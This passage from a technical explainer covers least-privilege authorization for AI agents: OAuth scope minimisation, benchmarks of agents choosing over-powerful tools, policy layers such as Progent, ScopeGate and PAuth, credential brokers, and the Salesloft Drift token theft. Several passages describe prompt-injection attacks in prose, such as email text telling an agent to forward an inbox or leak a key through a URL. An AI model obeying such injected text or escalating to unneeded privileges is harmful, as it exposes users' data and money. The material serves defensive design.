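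The models did well on Dropbox, where each method belongs to one scope, and worse on Google's deep hierarchies. The three stronger models rarely requested too little access, except on the two Outlook applications, and more often requested too much. For tasks that spanned several applications, GPT-5's scope sets permitted 12% more methods than MiniScope's on average, and Qwen3's permitted more than twice as many.

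MiniScope was also faster, adding 1% to 6% to the time an ordinary agent took. The largest increase, for one group of tasks, was from 4.91 to 5.23 seconds, or 6.5%, which may be why the study's introduction gives the range as 1% to 7%. With GPT-5 choosing the scopes, the same tasks took 20.5 seconds and cost an extra $0.063 per request, mostly because the model had to read the permission tables of every application involved.

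The burden on the user is harder to measure. When MiniScope needs another scope, the user can refuse it or allow it once, for the current session, or permanently. Zhu and colleagues simulated three months of Gmail requests with several kinds of user, and the share of requests that led to a confirmation ranged from 18% to 60%. A language model playing a security-conscious user had to confirm a quarter as often as when the system asked about each method separately. The simulation included no real people, so it can't show whether they would read the twentieth question as carefully as the first.

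A person who always clicks "Always allow" soon stops seeing permission prompts. By then the agent holds every scope it has ever requested, much like an agent whose grant grows through step-up authorization. Session permissions limit this buildup because MiniScope discards them when the conversation ends.

### How often programs request too much

Zhu and colleagues also used MiniScope to check the connectors in ChatGPT and Claude. They compared the permissions each connector requested with the smallest set that would support its advertised functions, and found six that requested more than they needed:

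| Connector | Methods permitted by the request | Methods permitted by the smallest set |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, Gmail | 50 | 32 |
| ChatGPT, Google Calendar | 12 | 5 |
| ChatGPT, Notion | 32 | 13 |
| ChatGPT, Dropbox | 44 | 25 |
| Claude, Google's file storage | 45 | 27 |
| Claude, Notion | 32 | 29 |

ChatGPT's Gmail and Calendar connectors were advertised only for reading, but their permissions also covered changing and deleting mail and events. Claude's file-storage connector was also advertised only for reading, but an optional scope gave it permission to change and delete files. The study dates from December 2025, and either company may have changed its connectors since. It doesn't show that either assistant ever used the extra permissions.

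Some websites were already requesting more than the minimum before agents became common. In *Everybody's Looking for SSOmething* (2023), Dimova, Van Goethem and Joosen used a program to search 100,000 popular websites in October 2021 for "log in with Google" buttons and similar OAuth logins. It found them on 6,211 sites. On 1,151 of those (18.53%), at least one button requested a "non-minimal" scope, one that goes beyond the least data the login provider can share.

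A non-minimal scope may still be necessary, since a dating site can have a good reason to ask for a user's age. Later papers sometimes confuse "non-minimal" with "unnecessary". *Proposal for Improving Google A2A Protocol* (Louck, Stulman and Dvir, 2025) cites the study as showing that 18.5% of OAuth deployments request unnecessary scopes and thereby violate the GDPR, the European Union's data protection law. The study's 18.53% figure doesn't show that the scopes were unnecessary or that requesting them violated the GDPR.

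Dimova and colleagues tested necessity separately. They chose 100 of the websites that requested non-minimal scopes, cut each request down to the minimum and tried to log in:

- On 65 sites, the login worked as before.
- On 24 sites, the login worked but the site then asked for the missing information. Eight of these asked for it even when they had received the full scopes, so they apparently weren't using the data.
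- On 11 sites, the login failed or led to an error message.

If those 100 sites are typical, about 12% of websites with OAuth logins requested scopes they didn't need for login. The researchers looked only at the first page after login, so some sites may have needed the data later. Logging in is also a much simpler task than running an agent, so the 12% figure can't be applied directly to agents. But a developer can use the same method for an agent by removing one scope at a time on a test account and checking whether the task still succeeds.

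The scopes a provider offers probably affect how much access developers request. Twitter offered only three levels of access, and 75% of the websites with a Twitter login asked for permission to write as well as read. Only 3% of websites with a Google login requested anything beyond the minimum.

### Tasks with no single smallest grant

MiniScope always returns one answer, even when more than one is right. Two sufficient grants can each permit something the other doesn't, so neither footprint contains the other. If both are also minimal, the definition of least privilege doesn't favor either. Mathematicians call a set of such alternatives an antichain.

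Xu's example is a task that reads information about a project in BigQuery, Google's data-analysis service. Two scopes are minimal and sufficient:

| Scope | Methods | Methods that change something | Services reached |
|---|---|---|---|
| bigquery | 286 | 144 | 10 |
| cloud-platform.read-only | 565 | 61 | 27 |

If the developer is mainly worried about a thief reading confidential data, the first scope is safer because it reaches fewer services. If the worry is that the agent might damage something, the second is safer. (Xu identified changes mainly from the HTTP method of each call, so some of the 61 "changes" in a read-only scope may be harmless.)

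MiniScope's standard cost would favour the bigquery scope, at 286 compared with 565 for the read-only scope. A developer who considers changes more serious could count each method that changes something as five. The costs would then be 862 for the bigquery scope and 809 for the read-only scope, which would favour the read-only scope. The result therefore depends on a judgement about risk that someone has to make before doing the calculation.

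Xu measured how common such tasks are using the permission tables that Google and Microsoft publish. The Google table covers 23,852 methods in 517 APIs. Of 2,822 tasks on Google's APIs, 3.2% had no single smallest grant. For Microsoft Graph, the API for Outlook, Teams and other Microsoft services, the share was 29.8% to 33.3%, depending on the type of access. The 33.3% figure comes from only 24 tasks, but the other two types of access had 450 or more tasks each and shares of about 30%.

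These percentages describe the tables better than they describe agents' work, because Xu generated the tasks from the tables. Each Google task consisted of every API method for one kind of record, such as calendar events. Each Microsoft task grouped operations whose addresses begin the same way. People's requests don't follow those groupings, so deployed agents might run into this problem more or less often.

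When a task has more than one minimal grant, the choice between them can matter a great deal. For example, one minimal grant for editing a message in a Microsoft Teams channel permits 6 operations, while another permits 265. In the two main types of Microsoft access, the largest alternative typically permitted more than three times as many operations as the smallest.

Microsoft gives most of its permissions a privilege level from 1 to 4, but these levels often can't be used to choose between two permissions. In those two types of access, the levels were equal for 67% and 74% of the pairs in which neither grant contained the other. In one pair, both permissions are at level 4, but one reaches 355 operations and the other reaches 11.

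Xu then tested how well six leading language models, each from a different company, chose among grants. In the first test, each model saw a task and the complete list of minimal grants for it. At first the models saw only the permissions' names, and later they also saw how many operations each grant allowed. In the second test, Xu added grants that were sufficient but larger than necessary, and told the models to choose the grant that gave the least additional authority.

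| Share of choices | Names only | Names and number of operations | Minimal and larger grants mixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fewest operations | 54.6% | 79.9% | 74.1% |
| Smallest on all four measures | 38.9% | 52.9% | 66.7% |
| Clearly worse than another option | 32.3% | 12.9% | 22.1% |

The four measures are the number of operations, the number that change something, the number of services, and whether the grant reaches administrative functions. A grant is clearly worse if another does at least as well on all four measures and better on at least one. Even a minimal grant can be clearly worse, because a grant of 355 operations may lack one of the 11 that a much smaller grant permits.

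In the mixed test, the models picked a minimal grant 99.0% of the time, but more than a fifth of their choices were clearly worse than another option. A benchmark that checked only for minimality would have missed this. The high score doesn't contradict the lower scores in Zhu and colleagues' test, because Xu's models chose from a finished list, while Zhu's were older and had to put the set together themselves.

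Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the grant. For the BigQuery task, that person could compare both scopes with their numbers and decide which risk is more acceptable. This seems practical for an administrator who sets up a company's agent once. Alice would probably find it tiresome during an ordinary request, so the developer should make such choices for her in advance. In the first test, adding the number of operations increased how often the narrowest scope was chosen by 25 percentage points, so the count is worth including wherever a person or a model has to choose.

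### Whether agents choose modest tools

The smallest set of scopes that covers a plan is still too broad if the plan includes a powerful operation the task doesn't need. MiniScope takes the plan from the agent, so it relies on the agent to choose tools no more powerful than the task requires.

*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) tested this with a benchmark called ToolPrivBench. It has 544 simulated tasks, each with three ordinary tools and three more powerful ones. Any of the six can complete the task alone. In one task, the agent must change an employee's manager. The ordinary tools use the company's personnel system, with its usual checks. One of the powerful tools writes directly to the database, and another uses master credentials to change every staff directory at once.

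The researchers made the ordinary tools return temporary errors, such as a failed connection, and gave each agent up to five turns. They counted a violation whenever an agent used a powerful tool before trying every ordinary one. Six of the eleven models did so in more than 30% of the tasks. The smaller open models Qwen3-8B and Llama-3.1-8B reached 64.9% and 55.9%, while Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%.

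Errors made agents much more likely to use powerful tools. GPT-5.2 started with one in only 5 of the 544 tasks. It switched to one after trying a single ordinary tool in another 13 tasks, and after trying two in 35 more.

Training models to refuse harmful requests did not reliably reduce their use of powerful tools. Yang and colleagues trained two small models this way, and both refused far more harmful requests. But one used powerful tools only slightly less often than before, and the other used them more. Training aimed directly at choosing less powerful tools worked better and reduced Qwen3-8B's rate of powerful tool use to 27%.

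In *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues tried a simpler remedy on the same 544 tasks in October 2026. They added a label to each tool's description that gave its type of access and a cost from 1 to 10, such as "administer, cost 9/10". A language model drafted the labels without knowing which tools the benchmark classed as powerful, and a person who checked a sample agreed with 82% of the access types.

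Eight models did the tasks with no help, with the labels, with an instruction to follow least privilege, and with both. The first four columns of figures show how often a model used a powerful tool before trying all the ordinary ones. The last two show how often it completed the task with only ordinary tools.

| Model | No help | Labels | Instruction | Both | Ordinary tools only, no help | Ordinary tools only, both |
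|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 56.6% | 40.6% | 29.8% | 16.2% | 6.4% | 12.7% |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 63.4% | 48.0% | 21.3% | 6.8% | 11.8% | 31.2% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 12.9% | 3.9% | 7.9% | 2.0% | 69.1% | 51.8% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 5.7% | 5.0% | 0.9% | 3.9% | 30.7% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 5.5% | 3.9% | 1.7% | 5.5% | 30.7% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 19.1% | 9.9% | 2.9% | 18.8% | 51.1% |
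| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 2.4% | 1.5% | 0.0% | 50.9% | 65.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 1.1% | 0.7% | 0.9% | 11.9% | 20.0% |

The labels reduced early use of powerful tools for every model except Claude, which had little room to improve. When Parkinson and colleagues replaced the labels with irrelevant notes about response times, no model improved significantly and two got worse. In a smaller test on two of the Qwen models, labels still helped when 30% of the costs were random.

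But the benchmark's count makes the labels look more effective than they are. An agent could try each ordinary tool once, get three errors and then use a powerful one without this counting as a violation. Each ordinary tool would have worked on the second attempt, so the powerful tool was still unnecessary. With the labels, DeepSeek's violations fell from 18.6% to 5.7%, but the share of tasks in which it used a powerful tool at any point rose from 62.9% to 71.3%. Combining the labels with the instruction to retry at the same level of privilege led models to complete many more tasks with ordinary tools alone.

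Some of the low violation rates also reflect unfinished work more than good judgement. Claude usually tried the three ordinary tools once each, then stopped and reported the errors, which is safe but leaves the user's job undone. It completed only 19.9% of the tasks without help. After an error, Llama often called tools that didn't exist, and the labels reduced its completion rate from 82.0% to 45.2%. These figures also depend on how the researchers run a model. Llama's violation rate without help was far below the 55.9% in the original study.

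The benchmark probably overstates how often agents use powerful tools in ordinary work, because only the less powerful tools fail in it. When Parkinson and colleagues removed the errors, Qwen3-8B used a powerful tool in 8.1% of the tasks and Qwen3-30B-A3B in 6.1%. But real services also fail, and the PocketOS agent deleted the database after it had a problem with login details.

Labels and instructions are easy enough to use in any agent, provided that the labels come from a source an attacker can't edit, but they still leave the decision to the model. A developer building an agent for one job can do better by leaving out unnecessary tools. If Alice's agent has tools only for listing messages, opening a message and creating an event, an error in Gmail can't lead it to plan a deletion, and its plan won't require a broader scope.

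## Limiting the amount, recipient and effect of each action

An agent that has only the tools it needs can still put the wrong values in a call. Suppose Alice asks an agent to send $100 to Bob. Her bank may offer a scope for making transfers, but that scope lets the agent send any amount to any recipient, any number of times. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) points out that the bank never learns what Alice asked for, so it can't tell the transfer she wanted from any other.

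Arguments are the values that a program supplies to an operation. A scope permits the operation with any arguments the agent chooses, but Alice meant to permit only one call, with Bob as the recipient and $100 as the amount.

### Why finer scopes are not enough

The bank could offer narrower scopes, such as "transfer up to $500", but it would need one for each combination of amount range, recipient and account to pay from. Ten ranges, 50 recipients and four accounts would require 2,000 scopes (10 × 50 × 4). Even then, an agent with the scope for up to $500 could send $499 when Alice asked for $100.

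Some values aren't known when the user gives consent. If Alice asks an agent to pay a quarter of her credit card balance, nobody knows the amount until the agent looks up the balance, possibly at another company. Sharma and colleagues conclude that no list of scopes written in advance can cover such a task.

### Fixed limits

A limit can be useful even if it allows more than the user requested. If Alice's agent can pay only Bob and her landlord, and never more than $500 at a time, a single mistaken payment costs her at most $500 and goes to someone she knows. Some services enforce limits like these themselves. If a service doesn't enforce a particular limit, such as the size of a refund made with a Stripe key, the developer's software has to.

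In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) audited the public code of three common agent frameworks, which are ready-made software for building agents and include the code that runs the model's tool calls. The three were LangChain (with its companion LangGraph), LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to Stripe's payment operations. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent has, but none checks by default whether the values in a particular call are acceptable.

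LangChain's code looks up the tool that the model named, usually checks that the inputs have the right format, and runs the tool. The format check wouldn't catch an attacker's account number, because that has the right format too. LlamaIndex works in much the same way. The Stripe toolkit passes on the amount, currency, customer and redirect address that the model chose, within the limits of the restricted key. Stripe's servers may apply further checks, which Mellafe Zuvic's audit didn't cover. The audit doesn't present these findings as vulnerabilities, because the frameworks leave such checks to the developer by design.

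To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a prepared tool call that redirected a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account in a simulated payment system. LangChain ran it. ScopeGate, a program that Mellafe Zuvic wrote to sit between the model and the tools, refused the same call. It asks four questions about every call:

1. Is the tool on the developer's list?
2. Are restricted arguments, such as the payout account, on a list of allowed values?
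3. For a payment or refund, is the amount a finite number between zero and a set ceiling?
4. If the developer requires one, does the call come with an idempotency key, an identifier that lets a service recognise a repeated request?

ScopeGate allows the call only if every answer is yes. If the check itself fails with an error, it refuses the call.

The third check is easy to get wrong. An early version of ScopeGate let through an amount of "NaN", a special value that computers use for "not a number". Any comparison with NaN is false, so the way a developer writes the rule matters:

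```
refuse if amount > 500               NaN gets through, since "NaN > 500" is false
allow only if 0 <= amount <= 500     NaN fails
```

In tests, ScopeGate refused all 48 prepared attempts to get around it. A language model that saw the reason for each refusal then made 29 unauthorised attempts over 40 rounds, and none succeeded. In another test, ScopeGate allowed all ten legitimate calls. The tests were small and used simulated payments, and ScopeGate's designer also designed them. They show that the checks work as intended, but not how well they would stop skilled attackers.

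A ceiling for each call doesn't limit the total. Ten refunds of $500 would all pass a $500 ceiling, so the developer also needs a daily budget or a limit on the number of calls per hour. Keeping count is harder when several copies of an agent run at once. If two copies share a $500 budget, both could see that nothing has been spent and each pay $400, for a total of $800. *Bounded Capability Receipts and Durable Spend Control for Agent Actions* (Schrock, 2026), a draft submitted to the IETF, notes that a signed token can't prevent this by itself and proposes a shared record in which an agent reserves money before it pays. Once the first copy had reserved $400, the second would find only $100 left and be unable to make its payment.

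### Progent: different rules for different tasks

Limits loose enough to allow every task are too loose for most of them. An agent needs to send email when Alice asks it to write to a colleague, but not when she asks only for a summary of her inbox. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a system designed for this problem, which checks each tool call against a policy that can change with the task.

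A policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under certain conditions on its arguments. In slightly simplified notation, a policy for Alice could look like this:

```
allow  events.insert  when { calendarId == "primary" and attendees.length == 0 }

forbid transfer       when { not amount <= 500 },
                      fallback: request user inspection

allow  transfer       when { recipient in ["bob-4471", "landlord-0932"] }
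```

Progent applies the "forbid" rules before the "allow" rules and blocks any call that matches neither. A $100 transfer to Bob goes through. A $600 transfer to Bob matches the "forbid" rule, so Progent asks Alice. A $100 transfer to a stranger matches neither rule, so Progent blocks it and returns an error message, which lets the agent continue with the rest of its task.

The first rule lets the agent create calendar events but not invite guests, so it can't use an event to send messages to other people. The agent also can't delete Thursday's budget review, because no rule allows deletion, even though its calendar token does. These limits work only if every call passes through Progent. If the agent can read the token, as in the PocketOS deletion, it can call the service directly.

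Writing a policy by hand for every request would take too long, so Progent has a language model write one from the user's task. The policy may have to change as the agent learns more. In an example from Shi and colleagues, a user asks an agent to do the tasks listed in a certain email:

1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email tells the agent to summarise the user's recent emails and post the summary on Slack, a workplace chat service. The language model proposes rules for reading mail and posting to Slack. These allow more than before, so someone has to approve them.
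3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, and the new policy allows posts to that person only. This allows less than before, so Progent applies it automatically.
4. One of the recent emails contains hostile text that tells the agent to forward the whole inbox to an attacker. No rule allows sending email, so Progent blocks the call.

Progent uses an SMT solver rather than a language model to check whether a new policy allows any call that the old one doesn't. An SMT solver is a program that can determine whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions. Progent replaces the old policy automatically only when the new one allows no additional calls.

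Mellafe Zuvic reasonably objects to any design in which a language model writes the limits, because the text that corrupts the call could also corrupt the limits. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI*, which assessed Progent in 2026, also warns that hostile text in a tool's result could loosen the policy, and adds that people make mistakes when they write policies by hand. Progent addresses the risk from hostile text by basing the first policy on the user's request, before the agent has read anything from outside, and requiring approval for every later loosening, so the protection depends on whoever approves the changes.

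Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a benchmark of attacks that use hostile text to redirect agents handling banking, messages, travel and office work. Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agents completed about as many tasks as they did without it. In this test, the researchers automatically approved every policy change to imitate a careless user. When they kept the initial policy unchanged, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. On a second benchmark, Progent reduced the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%, and most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools.

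Progent can't stop an attack that stays within the rules. If the user asks an agent to buy a kettle, a seller's hidden text can still persuade the agent to choose that seller's kettle, because the task requires a purchase and any kettle would satisfy the request.

### Rich Authorization Requests

The policy layers described so far run in the developer's software, so the service can't see their limits. An extension to OAuth lets the user approve exact values and the service enforce them. Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell (2023), in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, define a field called "authorization_details", which a client can send in place of a scope. Their main example is a bank transfer. In the same format, a request for Alice's payment to Bob could look like this:

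```
"authorization_details": [
  {
    "type": "payment_initiation",
    "creditorName": "Bob",
    "creditorAccount": {"id": "bob-4471"},
    "instructedAmount": {"amount": "100.00", "currency": "USD"},
    "locations": ["https://bank.example/transfers"]
  }
]
```

The authorization server shows the user the amount and the recipient. After the user agrees, it issues a token tied to these details, which the bank can read in the token or look up at the authorization server. The bank can then refuse any transfer for a different amount or to a different account. The user can also fill in details that the client left open, such as which account to pay from.

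The request normally passes through the user's browser, where someone could change it. To prevent this, the client can sign the request or send the details directly to the authorization server beforehand.

Each service defines its own types of request, so an agent that knows one bank's format may not be able to use another's. The standard also gives clients no way to look up a format. *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* (Zehavi, June 2026), a draft, proposes a way to do so and an error message that would list the missing details for the client.

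This object sets the amount but not the number of payments, and the token in the standard's sample response is valid for an hour. The bank therefore has to make sure an agent can't use such a token to pay Bob twice.

This approach suits a single important payment with known details. Sharma and colleagues object that in longer tasks the user would have to approve nearly every call. The client also needs to know the exact amount before it asks for approval. To pay a quarter of a credit card balance, it would first have to look up the balance and then come back to Alice for approval.

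### Credentials for a single purchase

Payment companies are building similar limits into the credentials that agents use to make purchases. Stripe's *Process payment credentials from an agent* describes a shared payment token, which is a reference to a stored payment method. The token works for one seller, up to a maximum amount and until a set time, and the seller never sees the card number. Stripe uses these tokens in the Agentic Commerce Protocol, a shopping standard it developed with OpenAI.

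A request for such a token, from Stripe's *Create a SharedPaymentIssuedToken*, includes these lines:

```
seller_details[network_business_profile] = {{NETWORK_BUSINESS_PROFILE}}
usage_limits[currency]   = usd
usage_limits[max_amount] = 1000
usage_limits[expires_at] = 1751587220
```

Stripe normally states amounts in cents, so the limit is $10. The token in Stripe's sample response expires 24 hours after it is created. Its record also shows how much the seller has charged so far, according to Stripe's *The Shared Payment Issued Token object*.

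These limits protect the buyer from a dishonest seller or a thief who copies the token. They offer less protection against a misled agent, because the agent's side chooses the seller and the maximum when it requests the token. If the model can fill in those fields freely, hostile text can change them. The developer's software should copy them from an order that the user has approved. The sample request also uses the account's secret key, which the model must not be able to access.

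Digital Commerce 360 (2026) reported in March that Affirm and Klarna, which let shoppers pay in instalments, were using shared payment tokens. Stripe's documentation still labelled the feature a private preview in June. Stripe can also obtain agent tokens from Mastercard and Visa that work at many sellers, according to American Banker's *Stripe advances security for agentic commerce*. These tokens are more convenient for an agent that compares shops, but they don't tie the payment to one seller in advance.

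Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) records the user's permission in signed documents called mandates. AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* describes a checkout mandate, which covers what the user is buying, and a linked payment mandate, which covers the payment. Both can serve as evidence in a dispute.

According to the blog No Hacks, an open mandate holds the user's conditions, such as running shoes for at most $120, and a closed mandate holds the final purchase. This lets an agent buy something while the user is away, which the FIDO Alliance describes as new in version 0.2. *AP2 Mandates*, part of the documentation for another shopping standard, the Universal Commerce Protocol (UCP), requires the checkout mandate to include the shop's full offer and signature, so nobody can change the price without invalidating a signature.

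Google announced AP2 in September 2025. *Google Donates Its Agentic Payments Protocol to the FIDO Alliance* (Nawrocki, 2026) reported on 30 April that Google was handing it over to the alliance, a nonprofit industry group. It's hard to tell how many shops use AP2. The August 2026 version of the Universal Commerce Protocol supports mandates only when both the shop and the agent's platform have opted in, and *AP2*, a guide from the software company Lumar, described adoption in July as "early pilots".

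A mandate can prove what the user agreed to, but an open mandate leaves the agent some choice, and hostile text can influence that choice. Mellafe Zuvic cites research on prompt injection against AP2 and argues that software should still check each payment against fixed rules before it goes through.

### PAuth: working out the exact call from the task

Sharma and colleagues propose a system called PAuth, in which each service works out for itself which call the user's task requires. Suppose Alice owes $400 on a Citi credit card and asks an agent to pay a quarter of it from her account at Chase, another bank:

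1. Alice signs the text of her task, and the agent's software sends it to both banks with a list of the operations they offer.
2. A language model at each bank translates the task into a short program. The model sees only the task and the list of operations, so hostile text in an email or on a web page can't reach it.
3. Ordinary software at Chase keeps only the part of the program that determines Chase's own transfer. Sharma and colleagues call the result a slice:

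```
Chase.transfer(Alice's Chase account, Alice's Citi card, Citi.getBalance(Alice) / 4)
```

4. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns it in an envelope, a signed record of the value and its origin:

```
value:      400
origin:     Citi.getBalance(Alice)
signed by:  Citi
```

5. The agent asks Chase to transfer $100 to the Citi card and attaches the envelope.
6. Chase verifies Citi's signature and divides 400 by 4. The result matches the requested amount, and the recipient matches the slice, so Chase makes the transfer.

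If the agent asks for $101 or names another recipient, Chase asks Alice whether she wants that transfer. The agent can't invent a higher balance, because it can't forge Citi's signature.

A slice can also include conditions. In one test, the user wanted the cheapest item in a shop, but only if it cost less than $80. The bank paid only if signed records from the shop showed that the item was within the budget and in the cart, and that the payment matched the cart's total.

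The table below shows how each limit would apply to four possible calls in Alice's task. The third column applies if Citi is on the list of recipients, and the fourth if Alice has approved exactly $100 to Citi.

| Call | Scope for transfers | $500 ceiling and list of recipients | Rich Authorization Request | PAuth |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| $100 to Citi | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| $101 to Citi | Allowed | Allowed | Refused | Chase asks Alice |
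| $100 to a stranger | Allowed | Refused | Refused | Chase asks Alice |
| A second $100 to Citi | Allowed | Allowed | Depends on the bank | Depends on the bank |

The last entry for PAuth is uncertain because Sharma and colleagues describe checking each call against the slice but don't mention counting how many times a call has already matched.

In a test on 100 tasks in banking, messaging, office work, travel and shopping, PAuth let every task run without an extra prompt to the user. The test also included 634 calls that departed from the tasks, for example by changing the amount, using an unrelated tool or skipping a condition. PAuth blocked all of them, which in this study means that it would have prompted the user for permission.

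The 100 tasks were clearly worded, many because the researchers had rewritten them. For example, one original task asked the agent to "check and update" a rent payment, and the rewritten version gave the amount. With the original wording, 71 tasks ran without PAuth asking the user any questions. PAuth asked the user about the other 29 because they were vague or referred to information elsewhere.

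PAuth also depends on several assumptions:

- Every participating service runs a language model that translates tasks correctly. GPT-4.1 did so for all 100 tasks, and three other models did so for the tasks they received. The translation cost between $0.002 and $0.038 per task on average, depending on the model, and each service has to pay for its own.
- The task is unambiguous.
- The user reads each task carefully before signing it.
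- Each service tells the truth about its own data. Citi, for instance, must report the correct balance.

The services also see the full text of the task, so Chase learns about every other errand that Alice included in it.

Alice's original task would be a poor fit for PAuth. The title and time of each event come from emails that a language model has to interpret, so the calendar service can't calculate them in advance and would have to ask her about every event. The agent could instead read the invitations first and write the details into a new task for her to sign. She would then have only one list to check, but she would have to notice anything the agent had added because of hostile text.

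PAuth requires changes at each service. Sharma and colleagues suggest that an organisation could start with a trusted go-between, a form of credential broker, that holds the OAuth tokens and does the checking.

### Asking a person to approve an action

Progent and PAuth both leave difficult cases to a person, so it matters how carefully people read what they approve. There is little evidence on this for single actions. Sharma and colleagues write that people who must confirm a stream of calls switch on automatic approval. This seems likely, but the paper gives no data. In one of Progent's tests, a person reviewed the first policy and every proposed loosening, and no attack succeeded. This shows that careful review can work, but not that a busy user would be as careful. MiniScope's confirmation rates of 18% to 60% came from simulated users.

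How many questions users get depends heavily on what the system asks about. In Sharma and colleagues' benchmark, 44 of the 100 tasks needed at least three calls and 26 needed at least five. Asking about each call would also show users intermediate results they had never specified. Progent needed approval for only 6% of its policy changes on AgentDojo. It makes sense to save questions for actions that are hard to undo, such as a payment to a new recipient.

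A request for the user's approval should show the exact recipient and amount, and the service or the broker should take both directly from the API call. If the model writes the request instead, it can be misled into describing a payment to a thief as a refund to a customer. The approval should cover only that call, so if the agent changes the account number after the user approves, the broker has to ask again.

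### Retries, delays and dry runs

Even a correct call can cause damage if it runs twice. Suppose the agent sends $100 to Bob and the connection drops before the bank answers. The agent doesn't know whether the payment went through. If it tries again, Bob may get $200, and if it doesn't, he may get nothing. An idempotency key solves this problem:

```
POST /transfers
Idempotency-Key: task-8812-step-3

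{"recipient": "bob-4471", "amount": "100.00", "currency": "USD"}
```

The bank stores the idempotency key with the result of the first request. If a second request arrives with the same key, the bank returns the stored result and doesn't pay again. The developer's software should create the key and reuse it for every retry, because if the model made up a new key each time, the bank would treat each attempt as a new payment. The service also has to support these keys, since a tool like ScopeGate only checks that a key is present.

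A delay, such as Railway's 48-hour wait before it deletes a volume, leaves time to cancel an action that was wrong from the start, but only if the agent's credential doesn't let it skip the wait. Gmail's scopes make this restriction possible, since gmail.modify doesn't allow immediate permanent deletion but full access does.

A dry run reports what a call would change without changing anything. For a deletion, it might list the affected files and show whether customers are using them. If a service doesn't offer dry runs, the developer's software can look up the target before passing on the call and block the call if the target is in the wrong place. In the PocketOS case, such a lookup should have shown that the volume was in production. The software should do the lookup immediately before the real call, since the data may change between the two.

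Nobody can take back an email once the recipient has read it, so any delay has to come before the email is sent. An agent can save its messages as drafts for Alice to send, or the broker can hold them for ten minutes so she can cancel them. The same applies to calendar invitations, because deleting an event doesn't undo the notification its guests have already received.

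## Storing, passing on and revoking credentials

The limits in a developer's own software work only as long as nobody can copy the agent's credential and call the service directly.

### Where credentials leak

The simplest ways to give an agent a key are to paste it into the model's instructions, save it in a file or put it in an environment variable, a named value that a program receives when it starts. All three let the agent access the key.

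A key in the model's conversation goes to the company that runs the model, and often into the developer's logs. The model can also repeat the key. For example, hostile text might tell an agent to open a web address on the attacker's server with the key added at the end, and the attacker could then read the key in the server's log.

A coding agent can find keys in files that have nothing to do with its task, as the PocketOS agent did. People also publish files containing keys by mistake. *Securing non-human identities*, by Hutchings, Bouhmad and Varley, cites a report by the security company GitGuardian that more than 28 million secrets appeared in public GitHub repositories in one year.

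Developers often use environment variables to keep keys out of their code. But a program normally passes its environment variables to any program it starts, so an agent that can run commands can usually list them with a single command.

### One call through a credential broker

A credential broker, such as MiniScope, keeps the real token away from the agent. Suppose Alice's agent wants to add the budget review to her calendar. It sends the broker this request:

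```
POST /call HTTP/1.1
Host: broker.example
Session: s-7f31

{
  "operation": "events.insert",
  "calendarId": "primary",
  "summary": "Budget review",
  "start": "2026-10-15T10:00:00+02:00",
  "end": "2026-10-15T11:00:00+02:00"
}
```

The value "s-7f31" is a session handle, a reference that only the broker can connect with a real credential. The broker then does the following:

1. It looks up the handle and finds Alice's name, the operations that this session allows and the time at which the session ends.
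2. It checks the operation and its values against the rules, which might forbid adding guests.
3. It fetches Alice's Google token from its encrypted store and renews it if it has expired.
4. It builds the request to Google, attaches the token and sends it.
5. It removes any credentials of its own from Google's answer and returns the rest to the agent.

In step 4, the broker has to choose the address itself. If the agent could supply it, hostile text could make the broker send Alice's token to an attacker's server. The broker also shouldn't send the token when a service redirects the request to another site.

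The handle is still a kind of credential, because anyone who copies it and can reach the broker can make the calls it allows. The developer can limit this risk by having the broker accept the handle only from the agent's machine and by ending the session when the task is done.

In *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents*, Zhu and Wang (2026) assume that every relevant call goes through the broker. An agent that finds another token in a file can use it to bypass the broker. The broker also can't determine whether Alice wanted a call that its rules permit, or reliably remove every password that a stranger has written into an email.

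The broker is also an attractive target, since it may hold every user's tokens. Encrypting the tokens helps if an attacker copies only the database, but not if the attacker can run code inside the broker, which has to decrypt the tokens to use them.

### The Salesloft Drift theft

The theft of tokens from Drift in 2025 shows how much harm a break-in at such a store can do. Drift is an AI chat agent that companies put on their websites. Its owner, the sales software company Salesloft, held OAuth tokens that connected Drift to its customers' other accounts. Many of these accounts were at Salesforce, where companies keep records about their own customers.

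Clari/Salesloft's *Trust Center* describes how the attackers got the tokens, based on an investigation by the Google-owned security company Mandiant:

1. Between March and June 2025, the attackers had access to Salesloft's GitHub account. They downloaded code, added a guest user and set up automated workflows.
2. They used GitHub personal access tokens to search for more credentials, and copied secrets from environment variables.
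3. They entered Drift's systems at Amazon Web Services (AWS) and took the OAuth tokens for its customers' accounts.
4. They used the tokens to read those customers' data.

Help Net Security's *Salesloft Drift data breach* notes that Salesloft did not say how the attackers got into its GitHub account. The attackers stole Drift's credentials and called the other services themselves. Nothing in these findings suggests that they tricked Drift's language model.

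Google's report on the attack, *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), dates the Salesforce thefts from 8 August to at least 18 August. The attackers exported large amounts of data and searched it for passwords and keys to other services. The Hacker News (2025) reported that Google knew of more than 700 organisations that might be affected, and in September it reported that 22 companies had confirmed an impact. The true number probably lies between these figures, since the first includes possible victims and the second only companies that had publicly confirmed an impact.

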